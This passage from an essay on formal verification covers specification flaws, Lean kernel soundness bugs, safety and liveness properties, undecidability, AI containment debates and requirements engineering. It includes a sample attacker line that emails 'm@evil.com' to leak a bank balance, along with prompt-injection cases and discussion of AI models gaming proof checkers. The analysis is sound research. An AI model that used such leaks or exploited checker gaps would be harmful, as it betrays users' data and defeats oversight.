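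*Vero* (2026), a benchmark for AI agents that build verified software, reports that people confirmed 38 defective specifications in 9 of 43 projects. No program could meet three of them, in the project verified_ironkv, because they allowed any way of comparing keys, even one that doesn't put them in a consistent order. Some of the 38 defects may exist only in the benchmark's versions of the projects.

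Other faults were in Lean's *kernel*, the proof checker on which everything else relies. On 22 July 2026 Lean (2026) released a fix for a bug that could make the kernel accept a proof of any statement, true or false. Patrick Hulin had found the bug with help from GPT-5.6 Sol, an OpenAI model. Three days later Ramana Kumar published an AI-assisted "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, a famous open problem about whole numbers. The disproof exploited another kernel bug. According to the Lean team, quoted by the forum user skybrian in *Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576*, the kernel had failed to check part of a definition, which was a mistake in the implementation and not in Lean's theory. The false proof also passed an older version of nanoda, an independently written checker, because that version had an unrelated bug.

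Lean released a fix on 28 July. In *Lean 4 kernel soundness bug*, Brossard (2026) advised people who use Lean for security-critical work to recheck their existing proofs. According to *Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$* (2026), a later release fixed three more soundness bugs that OpenAI had reported.

Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) describes a different fault. Lean's logical definition of one text-handling function gave an empty string where the compiled version gave the whole original text. The company used that contradiction to derive Fermat's Last Theorem in a few lines. The kernel was not at fault. The derivation works only if a proof uses the result of compiled code as evidence, and Lean lists this as an extra axiom when a user asks what the proof depends on.

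### The cases by layer

The layers overlap, because a proof assumes that the unverified code around the verified code works. In the table, "false assumption" covers only assumptions about the machine and its resources, and "unverified part" means code outside the proof.

| Layer | System | Fault |
|---|---|---|
| False assumption | seL4 | The hardware has timing channels that its description omits |
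| False assumption | Verdi | A function generated from verified code ran out of memory (1 bug) |
| False assumption | OpenAI's data infrastructure (not verified) | Hardware fault |
| Wrong or weak specification | CompCert | The PowerPC description omitted a size limit (2 bugs) |
| Wrong or weak specification | IronFleet, Chapar | The server could repeat requests; an assertion could never fail (2 bugs) |
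| Wrong or weak specification | Projects in *Vero* | Requirements that were false or that no program could meet (38 defects) |
| Wrong or weak specification | Checkers in *Zero-Trust Formal Methods* | Defects that reviewers found |
| Unverified part | CompCert | Front end (6 bugs) |
| Unverified part | Verdi, Chapar | Network and disk code (10 bugs) |
| Unverified part | lean-zip | Archive reader and Lean runtime (2 bugs) |
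| Unverified part | Checkers in *Zero-Trust Formal Methods* | Spurious proof where two components read the same text |
| Faulty checker | IronFleet | Build tool, verifier and prover package (3 bugs) |
| Faulty checker | Lean | Soundness bugs (5), and a mismatch between a definition and its compiled code |

In these cases, verified code never broke a proved property while the assumptions held and the checker worked. A valid proof guarantees this, so it is not evidence that verification is useful. The absence of certain kinds of bug is better evidence. CompCert had none of the optimisation bugs found in the other compilers, and the distributed systems had no protocol bugs. Fonseca and colleagues attribute this to redundancy, since a verified component can violate a verified property only if its developers make a mistake in the code and a matching mistake in the specification or the verifier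 that hides the first.

The checker bugs seem less worrying for a developer who writes proofs in good faith, because only specially constructed definitions triggered the kernel bugs of July 2026. The bugs matter more when the proof comes from a stranger, or from an AI model that may have searched for anything the checker would accept.

The sample is small, and people chose what to verify. Fonseca and colleagues studied only three systems, and none used multi-threaded concurrency, which is very hard to verify. They warn against comparing their bug count with that of the unverified systems, which are mature products with far more features and users. Csmith did not generate programs with floating-point numbers, strings or recursion, so six CPU-years of testing without a failure are not evidence of how CompCert handles those. The fuzzing of lean-zip lasted about 19 hours and mainly looked for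 crashes and memory faults.

Jones (2017), in *Empirical Study on the Correctness of, Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, objected that the fair comparison is between verified systems and systems that received the same resources but used other techniques. None of these studies made that comparison. They give good reason to think that verification removes the bugs it targets, but they don't show that the same effort put into testing and review would have removed fewer.

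## Which properties can be stated exactly?

Exact languages can express a great deal, even though some of the faulty specifications in the last section were written in them. One example covers most of their range, an AI assistant that reads its user's mail and calendar and answers requests by email. The user might want it never to write to anyone outside an approved list, to answer every request eventually, and to keep her secrets.

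### Inputs and outputs

The simplest properties relate each input to its output. If f is the function that a program computes, P a condition on inputs and Q the required relation, they have the form

for all x: if P(x), then Q(x, f(x))

or, in words, every permitted input gets an output that fits it. The repaired sorting specification has this form, with its two conditions combined in Q.

In an example from *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026), a language model extracts the postcode from a British address and inserts the space if it is missing. From "10 Downing Street, London SW1A2AA" it should return SW1A 2AA. A specification can require that the output, ignoring spaces, occurs in the input and has the format of a postcode, but the format is easy to misstate. The prompt describes a postcode as one or two letters, one or two digits, an optional space, a digit and two letters.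 SW1A 2AA doesn't fit this description because it has a letter after the first digit, and two of the four sample postcodes in the same prompt don't fit either. The language model returned the right answer anyway, but a checker built from the description would have rejected it.

### Safety and liveness

An email assistant keeps running after it computes an answer. In *Defining Liveness*, Alpern and Schneider (1985) treat a run of a system as an infinite sequence of states. They represent a run that ends by repeating its last state forever. A property is a set of runs, and a system has the property if all its possible runs are in the set.

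A *safety property*, in the technical sense, is one whose every violation shows up at some finite point of the run, after which nothing can repair it. Formally, if a run is not in the set, it has a finite beginning that no continuation can bring back into the set. The approved-list rule is a safety property. With A for the list, it is

always: if the assistant sends a message to r, then r ∈ A

If a rule forbids sending messages to strangers, one such message breaks it, and no later behavior can undo the violation. For ordinary software, *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives the example of a system that must not write to the network after reading from a file.

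*CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff et al., 2026) checks rules like these before an AI agent acts. An AI model writes the agent's plan as a short program, and a tool turns the program into states and transitions for a model checker. In one example, the plan is to read a chat channel, have a second AI model find Bob's address in the messages, and write to Bob. The formula requires every direct message the agent sends to have a trusted recipient. Bob's address comes from untrusted text, so the model checker finds a violation before the agent sends anything.

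A *liveness property* requires that something eventually happens. Formally, every finite beginning of a run has at least one continuation that is in the set. The assistant's duty to answer is

for every step i: if a request arrives at i, the assistant answers it at some step j > i

The rule that an assistant must eventually reply is exact, but no finite observation can refute it. After ten years of silence, the assistant might still reply tomorrow. Termination is the usual example of such a rule for ordinary programs. If the assistant must reply within one minute, the rule becomes a safety property, because a minute without a reply violates it.

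Alpern and Schneider proved that every property of single runs is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property.

1. Let S be the set of runs whose every finite beginning can continue to some run in P. S contains P, and it is a safety property, because a run outside S has a beginning from which P is out of reach.
2. Let L be the set of runs that are in P or outside S. A run that is in both S and L must be in P, so P is their intersection.
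3. L is a liveness property. Take any finite beginning. If it can continue to a run in P, that run is in L. If it can't, all its continuations are outside S, and so they are in L.

For the division program, let P be "finishes with the right answer". Then S is "never finishes with a wrong answer", which is partial correctness, and L is "finishes". Safety proofs use an invariant, as Hoare's did, and liveness proofs use something like Turing's quantity that cannot fall forever. The theorem is useful because its two parts match these two proof methods. Splitting a property in two would not be enough, since Alpern and Schneider also showed that any property is the intersection of two liveness properties, provided the system has more than one state.

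Splitting a formula in this way can also expose a mistake. One rule that Nikolaou and colleagues give a security agent is to confirm which computer is affected before cutting it off from the network. Their formula is "no isolation *until* confirmation", but in the standard semantics of their logic, "until" also requires confirmation to happen eventually. An agent that correctly dismisses a false alarm, without confirming or isolating anything, obeys the rule in English but violates the formula. Language models make translation errors too. *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a survey by Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), reports a benchmark on which only 24.8% to 34.2% of the models' translations from ordinary language into a formal planning language had the right meaning.

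### Permissions and limits

Access rules are safety properties as well. Clarkson and Schneider's version is, in words,

at every step i: the rights that the operation needs ⊆ the rights that its requester held at step i − 1

The "− 1" makes the formula use the rights held before the operation. If it used the rights held afterward, a program could grant itself permission through the same operation that required it. Operating systems apply such rules to files, and the email assistant might have the right to read the calendar but not to delete entries. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025) offers a small formal language for rules on an agent's tool calls, with operators such as Before, After and Forall.

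Resource limits are also broken at a definite moment. The 51st message in a day breaks a limit of 50 messages a day, and the first byte over 2 gigabytes breaks a 2-gigabyte memory limit. But the mathematical description has to include the resource, or a proof won't rule out failures like Verdi's memory crash.

There is demand for such rules. Gekker, Steratore and colleagues (*AI Security Priorities*, 2026) asked more than 20 experts what AI security needs most. Permission frameworks for agents came third and formal verification of security properties ninth. These rankings reflect opinions, and some of the paper's authors work for companies that sell related services.

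### Secrets need more than one run

*Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) uses a scheduling assistant that may share when its user is free but not why she is busy. Suppose she is busy on Tuesday and free on Monday and Thursday, and a colleague asks for a meeting. The assistant offers Monday if Tuesday's appointment is an ordinary meeting, and Thursday if it is a confidential job interview. Both offers are true and neither mentions an interview, but a colleague who knew the assistant's habits could infer the interview from the offer of Thursday.

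The fault is in the relation between the two runs. Clarkson and Schneider call a property of a whole set of runs a *hyperproperty*. If T is the set of all possible runs of the assistant, the rule is

for all t and t′ in T: if public(t) = public(t′) and allowed(t) = allowed(t′), then output(t) = output(t′)

Here "public" means the inputs that aren't secret, such as the colleague's request, "allowed" means the information the user agreed to share, and "output" means what outsiders see. Without the clause about allowed information, this is one form of *noninterference*, the requirement that secrets have no effect on public output. A single run can never violate the property, because the property compares the outputs of two runs. A guard that checks one run at a time must therefore either miss these leaks or raise false alarms.

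Garby and colleagues give an example in ordinary code, which an attacker might trick a bank customer's agent into running:

`if account.balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")`

The message doesn't contain the balance, so a filter that searched outgoing mail for it would find nothing. But the attacker can still learn whether the balance is above the threshold, because an email arrives exactly when it is.

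The formula must also specify what an outsider can observe. *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026) compares the complete sequences of values that a program publishes for two different secrets, but not their timing, so a program would pass even if it published the same report an hour later for one of the secrets. seL4's confidentiality proof also leaves out timing leaks.

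Restricting a system can make it violate some hyperproperties that it satisfied before. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that may output 0, 1 or a secret bit h. It satisfies the rule that the *possible* outputs don't depend on the secret, since both 0 and 1 are possible whatever h is. If a developer removes the first two options, the system always outputs h and breaks the rule. The approved-list rule doesn't have this problem, because if all runs of an assistant obey it, they still do after a developer removes some of the assistant's options. Neither does the pairwise formula above, because removing runs only removes pairs that might violate it.

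Their other main example is average response time. If the mean over all runs must be at most one second, whether a five-second answer is acceptable depends on the other runs. Their formula puts the response times of all runs into a set and takes its mean. Read literally, this repeats the sorting specification's mistake about duplicates, because a set contains each number only once. Nine answers in 0.5 seconds and one in 5 seconds have a mean of 0.95, but the mean of the set {0.5, 5} is 2.75. Counting every occurrence of each response time fixes this. The formula would still need probabilities to avoid giving a run that happens once a year the same weight as one that happens every minute.

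### Probabilities need a distribution

The AI model inside the assistant chooses its words partly at random, and nobody knows which requests will arrive. Instead of requiring that the assistant never fail, a developer might require

Pr(the assistant fails on x) ≤ ε, where x is drawn from D

D is a probability distribution over requests, and ε is a small number such as 0.001. Ordinary software has probabilistic requirements too. Clarkson and Schneider mention a system that splits a secret among several servers and must, with high probability, refresh the pieces within a given time.

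Without D, the formula is neither true nor false. Suppose the assistant picks the wrong recipient for half of the requests that mention a name shared by two contacts, and makes no other mistakes. Its failure probability then depends on how many of the requests it receives are of this kind. If one in 1,000 is, the failure probability is 0.0005, which is within the limit. In an office where one in ten is, it is 0.05, or fifty times the limit. An attacker who writes all the requests can raise it to 0.5.

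A developer can avoid choosing D by requiring the limit to hold in every situation separately. *PACE* (2026) describes an agent's behaviour as a family of probability distributions, one for each context, where a context includes the request, tool results and any text an attacker has inserted. The requirement is then "for every context c, the probability of failure in c is at most ε", where the probability is taken only over the agent's own random choices. This is much stricter than averaging over D, and the assistant with the ambiguous names fails it. *PACE* notes that no audit of an agent's tool descriptions can list all the contexts.

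The developer must also specify the period that ε covers. If each request fails independently with probability 0.001, the chance of at least one failure in 1,000 requests is 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰⁰, or about 63%.

Randomness also changes the rule about secrets. Two runs of the scheduling assistant may now differ by chance, so one pair of different offers doesn't prove that the secret leaked. *Probabilistic noninterference* requires every public output to have the same probability whatever the secret is, so that seeing the output reveals nothing about the secret. An assistant that offers Thursday 50% of the time for an ordinary meeting and 80% of the time for an interview violates this requirement, because a Thursday offer is evidence of an interview. Garby and colleagues proved a version of this property for all programs in a small language for AI agents. Their version doesn't cover what an observer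 could learn from whether the program finishes.

### Two meanings of "safety"

The technical definition of a safety property does not mention harm. For example, "the assistant never uses the letter e" is a safety property. Alpern and Schneider informally described a safety property as the absence of a "bad thing", but their definition only requires that the bad thing, if it happens, happen at an identifiable point. They thought it naive to hope to prove such a definition correct, because good and bad things are "not well-defined concepts".

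An assistant that never sends anything obeys the approved list, the access rules and the message limit, and it leaks no secrets by email. But its silence could do serious harm if the user's doctor is waiting for an answer to an urgent question. Conversely, an assistant that sends a birthday greeting to a friend who isn't on the list yet violates a safety property but harms nobody.

Liveness properties catch some harmful omissions. For example, one of the faulty plans that Nikolaou and colleagues tested never isolates the infected computer, so it fails their requirement that isolation eventually occur. But in 22 of the 97 everyday tasks they ran with Claude Haiku 4.5, a small AI model, the plan passed the security checks of both CaMeLoT and the older system it extends and still didn't do what the user wanted.

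The literature on AI agents adds to the confusion over the term "safety property". Dantas and colleagues define a safety property of an agent's plan as any formula in certain temporal logics, which are formal languages with operators such as "always" and "eventually", so "eventually answers each request" counts as a safety property.

The user may also want the assistant never to send a misleading message. This looks just like the approved-list rule:

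always: if the assistant sends m, then m is not misleading

But the formula has no exact meaning until somebody defines "misleading" as a condition on messages and their circumstances. A developer could replace it with an exact condition, such as requiring every date in the message to match the company's records. The assistant could meet that condition and still mislead a customer by telling her that her parcel left the warehouse on Monday without mentioning that it came back on Tuesday.

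## Can every exactly stated property be checked?

The rule that an email assistant may write only to people on an approved list can be stated as an exact formula. Suppose the assistant also writes small programs, and its owner wants to check each one against the rule before running it. No algorithm can correctly determine, for every program, whether it will ever email someone who isn't on the list. A question is *decidable* if some algorithm always finishes with the correct answer, and *undecidable* otherwise. The email rule is an example of a property that can be stated exactly but is undecidable.

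### The halting problem

In 1936 Turing proved that no algorithm can solve the *halting problem*, which is to determine, for every program and input, whether the program eventually stops. Suppose an algorithm D could do this. Then we could write a program G that takes a program's text as input and uses D to determine whether that program halts when given its own text. If D's answer is yes, G loops forever, and if it is no, G stops. When G runs on its own text, it therefore does the opposite of D's answer, so D is wrong about G and can't exist.

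The approved-list rule has the same problem. Suppose an algorithm S could decide whether any given program ever emails a stranger.

1. Take any program M and any input w.
2. Write a new program that first runs M on w, in a simulation that cannot send email, and then emails a stranger.
3. If M halts on w, the new program reaches its second instruction and breaks the rule. If M never halts, the new program never gets that far, and so it obeys the rule.
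4. S's answer about the new program therefore also settles whether M halts on w. Since no algorithm can settle that for every M and w, S can't exist.

### Rice's theorem

In 1953, Henry Gordon Rice proved a much more general result about properties of the function that a program computes. In a programming language that can express any computation, if at least one program has such a property and at least one lacks it, no algorithm can decide for every program whether it has the property.

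The proof reuses the trick above. If a program that loops forever on every input has the property, let q be a program that lacks it; otherwise, let q be a program that has it. For any M and w, we can write a program that silently runs M on w and then does whatever q does. This program computes the same function as the endless loop if M never halts on w, and the same function as q if M halts. An algorithm that decided the property would therefore solve the halting problem.

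The property must concern what programs do, not how they are written. Gumbau Mezquita (2026), in *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic*, gives the example of whether a Turing machine's description has at most 100 states, which anyone can check by counting. Checking that a program's text contains no instruction for sending email is equally easy, and a program without one can't break the approved-list rule.

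The theorem is also about algorithms that must work for every program. For any single program, one of two trivial algorithms, "print yes" or "print no", gives the right answer, and the difficulty is finding out which.

### A program that waits for a counterexample

Goldbach's conjecture, from 1742, states that every even number greater than 2 is the sum of two primes. Pérez-Acle describes a program that checks each even number from 4 upward and performs a forbidden action if it finds one that is not such a sum. The program is safe exactly when the conjecture is true, and nobody knows whether it is.

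Testing helps little, because there is no counterexample below 4 × 10¹⁸. Pérez-Acle's test covered the even numbers up to 2,000,004 and revealed no violation. The same test did reveal a violation in a similar program based on the false conjecture that every square is below one million.

Such programs can be very small. *A Relatively Small Turing Machine Whose Behavior Is Independent of Set Theory* (2016) presents a Turing machine with 4,888 states that halts exactly when Goldbach's conjecture is false. *Determination of the fifth Busy Beaver value* (2025) mentions a 25-state version whose construction has been proved correct in Lean. Nobody knows whether this smaller machine ever halts, even though the proof confirms that it searches for a counterexample to the conjecture.

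But an individual hard case can be settled even when the general question is undecidable. *Hardness of busy beaver value BB(15)* (2021) mentions a 5,372-state machine that halts exactly when the Riemann hypothesis, a conjecture about the distribution of primes, is false. In November 2026 Levent Alpöge, a mathematician at Anthropic who had worked with the AI model Claude, released a proof of the hypothesis in 17 million lines of Lean. A day later, the Lean and Mathlib communities' *Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026) certified it as correct. If the proof is correct, the machine runs forever. Techno-Science's *An AI solves the Riemann hypothesis* notes that the Clay Mathematics Institute, which offers a prize for a proof, also requires publication and a wait of at least two years.

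### Which answers can be confirmed

A checker that can't always answer might still be useful if it could eventually confirm every program that has the property. Pérez-Acle calls a category of programs *confirmable* if some algorithm eventually accepts every program in it and never accepts one outside it. The algorithm may run forever on programs outside the category.

Requiring proofs doesn't get around this limit. A computer can check every possible proof one by one. If some sound proof system had a proof of safety for every safe program, this search would eventually confirm every safe program, which the limit rules out. The limit therefore applies to Hoare's rules and to Lean.

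Pérez-Acle worked out what can be confirmed for a prohibition, a confidentiality rule and a duty to respond. As in the previous section, the confidentiality rule does not cover timing.

| Requirement | Are the violators confirmable? | Are the compliant programs confirmable? |
|---|---|---|
| Never perform the forbidden action | Yes, by running the program until it does | No |
| Publish the same values for both secrets | No | No |
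| Eventually answer every input | No | No |

A "no" means that no algorithm works for every program in the category, though people can still prove things about many of them. For the prohibition, the "no" follows from the reduction above. For confidentiality, suppose a program has published a 0 in one run and nothing yet in the other. The second run may later publish a 0 too, or it may never publish anything, and no algorithm can always tell which.

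The requirement that a program respond to every input needs a different construction. Given a program M and an input w, we can build a second program that takes a number n and runs M on w for n steps. If M has halted by then, the second program loops forever. Otherwise it answers 0. The second program therefore answers every input exactly when M never halts on w. If M halts after a million steps, the second program answers every input below a million and no others.

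These failures have a common reason. Pérez-Acle proves that, for rules about visible behaviour, a category is confirmable only if a finite record of events can establish that a program belongs to it. A finite record can show that a program sent an email, but not that it will never send one.

Any sound method of certifying safe programs also fails to certify a safe program that is easy to describe. This program searches for a certificate of its own safety and performs the forbidden action if it finds one. If the method certified the program, the program would find the certificate and act, making the certificate false. A sound method therefore can't certify it, so the program never acts and is safe. Pérez-Acle built such programs for four simple certifiers, and each was only about 940 characters longer than the certifier that failed to certify it.

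### What a time limit costs

If a program may run for at most T steps, a checker can run it for T steps in a *sandbox*, an isolated environment where its actions have no outside effect, to decide whether it breaks a rule. Pérez-Acle proves that no method, including predicting the result from the program's text, can be both always right and always much faster than running the program.

The proof uses a program that runs the checker on the program's own text and then does the opposite of what the checker predicted. If the checker finishes early enough for the program to act within its T steps, the prediction is wrong. A checker that is right about every program must therefore sometimes run for roughly as long as the program could. In a simulation with eight checkers and eight time limits, only the checker that ran each program for the full time was right about the program written to contradict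 it. The other seven, including one that ran the program for half the time and one that flipped a coin, were wrong every time.

### Refusing some safe programs

In practice a checker doesn't have to classify every program. Let P be the set of permitted programs and O the set that the checker's owner has an obligation to admit, such as programs in a certain simple form. The checker then needs to admit some set A with

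O ⊆ A ⊆ P

so that it meets every obligation and admits nothing forbidden. Pérez-Acle's *admission theorem* states that a checker that always answers can do this exactly when some decidable set A fits between O and P. If the checker may keep some programs waiting forever, a confirmable set is enough. But if O contains every permitted program, A must equal P, and the undecidability returns.

Engineers already build checkers this way. The verifier for eBPF, a system for adding small programs to the core of an operating system, admits only programs it can prove safe. In *proof-carrying code*, each program arrives with a proof that the receiver checks. Type checkers also reject some programs that would run without error.

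The drawback is that the checker rejects some safe programs. Pérez-Acle measured how often this happens with a very crude rule, which accepts a machine only if its description never includes the forbidden action. In a simple design, the rule accepted 71.9% of all safe machines with three states, but only 47.3% of those with five. A cleverer rule would accept more, and machines this small can also be checked exactly.

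Most ordinary programs are not hard to check. Pérez-Acle generated 2.2 million random programs of 4 to 24 instructions. Of those whose status was clear, 1.6% broke the prohibition. A test that ran each program for 8 steps missed 30.2% of the violators with 24 instructions. A 64-step test missed two violators in the whole collection, and a 128-step test missed none.

At every limit from 64 to 4,096 steps, the confidentiality test wrongly rejected a small share of the compliant programs, up to 0.37% for the longest. Pérez-Acle examined the programs rejected at 1,024 and 4,096 steps. Each published the same endless sequence for both secrets but at different speeds, so one run was always ahead when the test stopped.

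These numbers are reassuring about accidental failures, at least for programs that resemble random ones. They offer little reassurance about an AI model that has a reason to get a particular program past the checker, because the model could write the kind of program on which the checker fails.

### Can a superintelligence be contained?

Several papers have used these theorems to argue that nobody can verify or control advanced AI. *Superintelligence cannot be contained* (Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues, 2016) is the best known, and the *Journal of Artificial Intelligence Research* later published it. The other AI papers discussed here, and Pérez-Acle's, appear to be only preprints.

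Alfonseca and colleagues use the reduction above with "harm humans" in place of "email a stranger". That reduction is about all programs, but a superintelligent AI would be one particular machine, so they assume that the machine can simulate any Turing machine, that its inputs can include any program, and that it has at least one operation that harms people. If such a machine carries out whatever program it receives, no algorithm can decide for every input whether it will do harm, even though the machine is fixed.

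In its *Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021), the Centre for the Study of Existential Risk at Cambridge argued that engineers don't study arbitrary programs. The Centre drew an analogy with mathematics, where no procedure can prove or refute every statement, but people can still prove Pythagoras' theorem. Similarly, engineers can write programs to be easy to verify, and they could design an AI that doesn't execute arbitrary subroutines.

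Alfonseca and colleagues had already rejected restrictions of this kind. They wrote that a superintelligent machine would use a Turing-complete language, which can express any computation, and would take the state of the world as input. They thought problems such as epidemics and climate change could not be solved within the limits formal verification imposes. Their point about language is weak, because Hoare's division program is also in a Turing-complete language, and its proof takes four steps. Their point about the world is stronger, because a proof would have to cover every situation the machine might meet. That may be hopelessly difficult, but the halting problem doesn't show that it is impossible.

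The impossibility result also depends on their definition of containment. The control strategy must stop the machine when there is reason to predict harm and allow it to act otherwise, so a strategy that also blocks some harmless actions doesn't count. Without the second requirement, containment is possible. A machine that can simulate any program but can't act on the outside world is contained, and their own proof assumes that an isolated Turing machine can't hurt anyone. However, such a machine may not be much use.

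To illustrate how hard such questions are, Alfonseca and colleagues mentioned about 40 five-state Turing machines that experts believed, but had not proved, would run forever. *Determination of the fifth Busy Beaver value* has since settled the five-state case, but hard cases remain among six-state machines.

CSER conceded that complex programs may still be unpredictable in practice. Its reply therefore supports research on verification but doesn't show that anyone can verify an advanced AI. To show this, somebody would have to build an AI that is both capable and easy to check.

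### Systems that change themselves

A proof about a program may not apply after the program rewrites itself. Gumbau Mezquita proves that no algorithm can determine, for every system, whether a safety property will still hold after the next rewrite. The proof applies Rice's theorem to the property of staying safe, and assumes that a general AI can express any computation and modify itself without restriction. Gumbau Mezquita concludes that people can certify lasting safety only for systems whose behaviour has stopped changing.

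This conclusion holds only if the rewrites are unrestricted. Developers could require a proof that each new version keeps the safety property before the system adopts it. The system would miss some safe improvements, but it could keep changing. Gumbau Mezquita discusses proof-carrying code and similar measures, and says they sacrifice generality or something else people want. So part of the disagreement is about how much an AI can be restricted and still count as "general".

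*The Self-Improvement Problem* (2026) acknowledges that its theorem about certifying improvements is close to a restatement of Rice's theorem. It adds an explicit construction of a proposed change that is good if the certifier rejects it and bad if the certifier accepts it. It also proves that no algorithm can always find an improvement among the proposals a program generates, even when one exists and the algorithm can read the program's code.

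### Trust and complexity

Panigrahy and Sharan (2025), in *Limitations on Accurate, Trusted, Human-level Reasoning*, argue that an AI system can't have all three qualities in their title. Under their strict definitions, an *accurate* system never makes a false claim, though it may answer "don't know". People *trust* it if they assume it is accurate. It reasons at *human level* if it can solve every problem for which a human has a provably correct solution.

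In the simplest version of the proof, the system A always finishes and judges whether programs halt. One can write a program that runs A on the program's own text, loops forever if A answers "halts", and stops otherwise. If A is accurate, it can't answer "halts", so the program stops. People who trust A can follow this argument and conclude that the program halts, but A can never give that answer.

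But people reach their conclusion only by assuming that A is accurate. Without that assumption, they have proved only that *if* A is accurate, the program halts, and nothing in the argument prevents A from proving that too. Another AI system that assumed A was accurate could also give the answer that A can't give. The theorem is therefore weak evidence of a general human advantage, because it concerns a system and a program built to contradict it. Panigrahy and Sharan note that their result doesn't rule out combining the three qualities under looser definitions.

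Hasan (2026), in *Incompleteness of AI Safety Verification via Kolmogorov Complexity*, starts from a different theorem. The *Kolmogorov complexity* of a string is the length of the shortest program that outputs it. Hasan encodes an input, the AI's output and a policy as a single string x, and assumes that a fixed fraction of strings, for infinitely many lengths, comply with their policy. The theorem is that every sound proof system has its own threshold, and for any n above that threshold the system can't prove a statement of the form

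x complies with the policy, and the complexity of x is greater than n

If it could, a short program could search through all proofs until it found such a statement and then output x. That program would be a description of x much shorter than n, which contradicts the statement.

Hasan infers that no fixed verifier can certify all compliant cases of high complexity. This doesn't follow, because a proof system that can't prove a case has high complexity may still be able to prove that it complies. For example, if the policy requires a binary string x to end in 0, half of all strings comply and many of them have very high complexity, but a verifier can check every one by looking at the last digit.

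### Finite but too large

All these theorems assume unlimited time and memory, and no real computer has either. A machine with m bits of memory has 2ᵐ possible states, so a program that runs on it without outside input or randomness must repeat a state within 2ᵐ steps and then loop. In principle, people can therefore decide everything about the program's behaviour by watching it for that long. With one kilobyte of memory, 2ᵐ is about 10²⁴⁶⁶. Pérez-Acle's result about time limits also applies here. It implies that a checker that is right about every such program needs a number of steps roughly proportional to 2ᵐ in the worst case.

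Gumbau Mezquita also answers the appeal to finiteness by pointing out that no algorithm can confirm every statement that is true in all finite structures, however large. This matters to someone who wants a guarantee for hardware of any size, but less for a machine with a known amount of memory, because rewriting its software doesn't increase the number of states it can be in.

The number of cases grows quickly even in conventional software. Symons and Horner (2019), in *Why there is no general solution to the problem of software verification*, remark that engineers in effect set the halting problem aside as a special case, but testing still can't cover every path. A 1,000-line program with a two-way choice every ten lines has 2¹⁰⁰ paths, or about 10³⁰.

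For a language model the numbers are far larger. Such a model reads text as *tokens*, which are words or pieces of words. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, the number of possible inputs of exactly 1,000 tokens is

100,000¹⁰⁰⁰ = (10⁵)¹⁰⁰⁰ = 10⁵⁰⁰⁰

A computer that checked 10¹⁸ inputs per second for ten billion years would cover only about 3 × 10³⁵ of the 10⁵⁰⁰⁰ possible inputs. Most of those inputs are gibberish, but restricting the check to sensible text would require an exact definition of sensible text and would still leave far too many to check.

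A property can be provable even when it covers a large number of inputs. Hoare's division theorem covers infinitely many inputs because one invariant holds on every pass through the loop, whatever the numbers are. A proof about a language model would need some comparable regularity in its billions of weights, and nobody designed the weights to have one.

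## How does a specification connect to the world outside the machine?

Even a proof that covers every possible input is only about the signals that enter and leave a machine, but people usually want something to be true of the world beyond those signals. *The meaning of requirements* (Jackson, 1997) gives the example of a lift whose owner wants the car to come to the floor where someone has pressed the button. The computer that controls the lift can only read sensors in the shaft and switch a motor on and off, so it can't move the car directly.

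Pamela Zave and Michael Jackson set out the standard account of this situation in "Four Dark Corners of Requirements Engineering", also from 1997. Zave writes that, for requirements, the environment is not the most important thing but "the only thing".

### Requirement, assumptions and specification

Their account separates three descriptions:

- R, the requirement, is a condition that people want to hold in the world, such as the lift coming when someone calls it.
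- W, the environment assumptions, describes how the world behaves whatever the machine does. For the lift, W includes the statement that the car starts to rise within 0.2 seconds once the motor is running upwards.
- S, the specification, describes what the machine must do. It mentions only events and states that the machine shares with its surroundings, such as the motor switch and the sensors.

The developers then have to show that

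W, S ⊢ R

The sign ⊢ means that R follows from W and S by logic, with no further knowledge of the world. *A reference model for requirements engineering*, a set of course slides by Godfrey, Berry and Trefler (2023), calls this the Zave–Jackson Validation Formula. The deduction can be checked by proof, but validation means finding out whether W is true and whether people want R.

R and S express wishes, while W states facts, a distinction Jackson describes with the grammatical terms *optative* and *indicative*. If a document mixes the two, a programmer who reads "the barrier does not move when locked" can't tell whether to make this true or assume it already is. W must also describe the world as it will be once the machine is running, which is hard to predict when people change their habits in response. Jackson cites traffic patterns as a notorious example.

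Jackson and Zave (1995), in *Deriving Specifications from Requirements*, work through the turnstile of a zoo. R is that the number of entries never exceeds the number of coins paid. The machine can detect coins and pushes on the barrier, and it can lock and unlock the barrier, but it can't detect entries. W includes two facts about the mechanism: pushes and entries alternate, starting with a push, and nobody can push a locked barrier. A specification that suffices is to keep the barrier locked whenever the number of pushes equals the number of coins. The proof is then one line:

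entries ≤ pushes ≤ coins

The first inequality holds because every entry needs its own push, and the second because the machine allows a push only when there is an unused coin. Trying to prove this also shows that W is missing an assumption. The machine needs a moment to lock the barrier again after the last paid push, so W must include a minimum time between one push and the next.

Some requirements can be stated exactly but cannot be met by any machine in its given surroundings. Jackson imagines a customer who wants the lift to cancel a request if the passenger who made it gets out early. This is easy to write as a formula, but an ordinary lift cannot detect which passenger pressed which button, so no specification can meet the requirement unless the lift itself is changed.

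Once the developers have S, the programmer can work from it without knowing anything about zoos. Dijkstra called a specification a logical "firewall" between the question of whether people would like an engine that meets it and the question of how to build one. Jackson gave S a similar role in 1997, but in *Engineering and Software Engineering*, which revisits Dijkstra's twenty-year-old remark, he argues that software and its surroundings are inseparable. The turnstile example partly supports both views, because a programmer could write the locking program from S alone, but nobody could have chosen S without studying the barrier.

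### Designations

The formulas about the turnstile contain terms such as Enter(e), and logic doesn't determine what they refer to. A *designation* connects a formal term to things in the world through an informal rule for recognising them. Under Jackson and Zave's designation, Enter(e) is true when e is the event of someone getting into the zoo by pushing the barrier as far as it goes. Someone who climbs over the barrier gets in without paying, but no Enter event occurs, so the theorem about entries and coins remains true.

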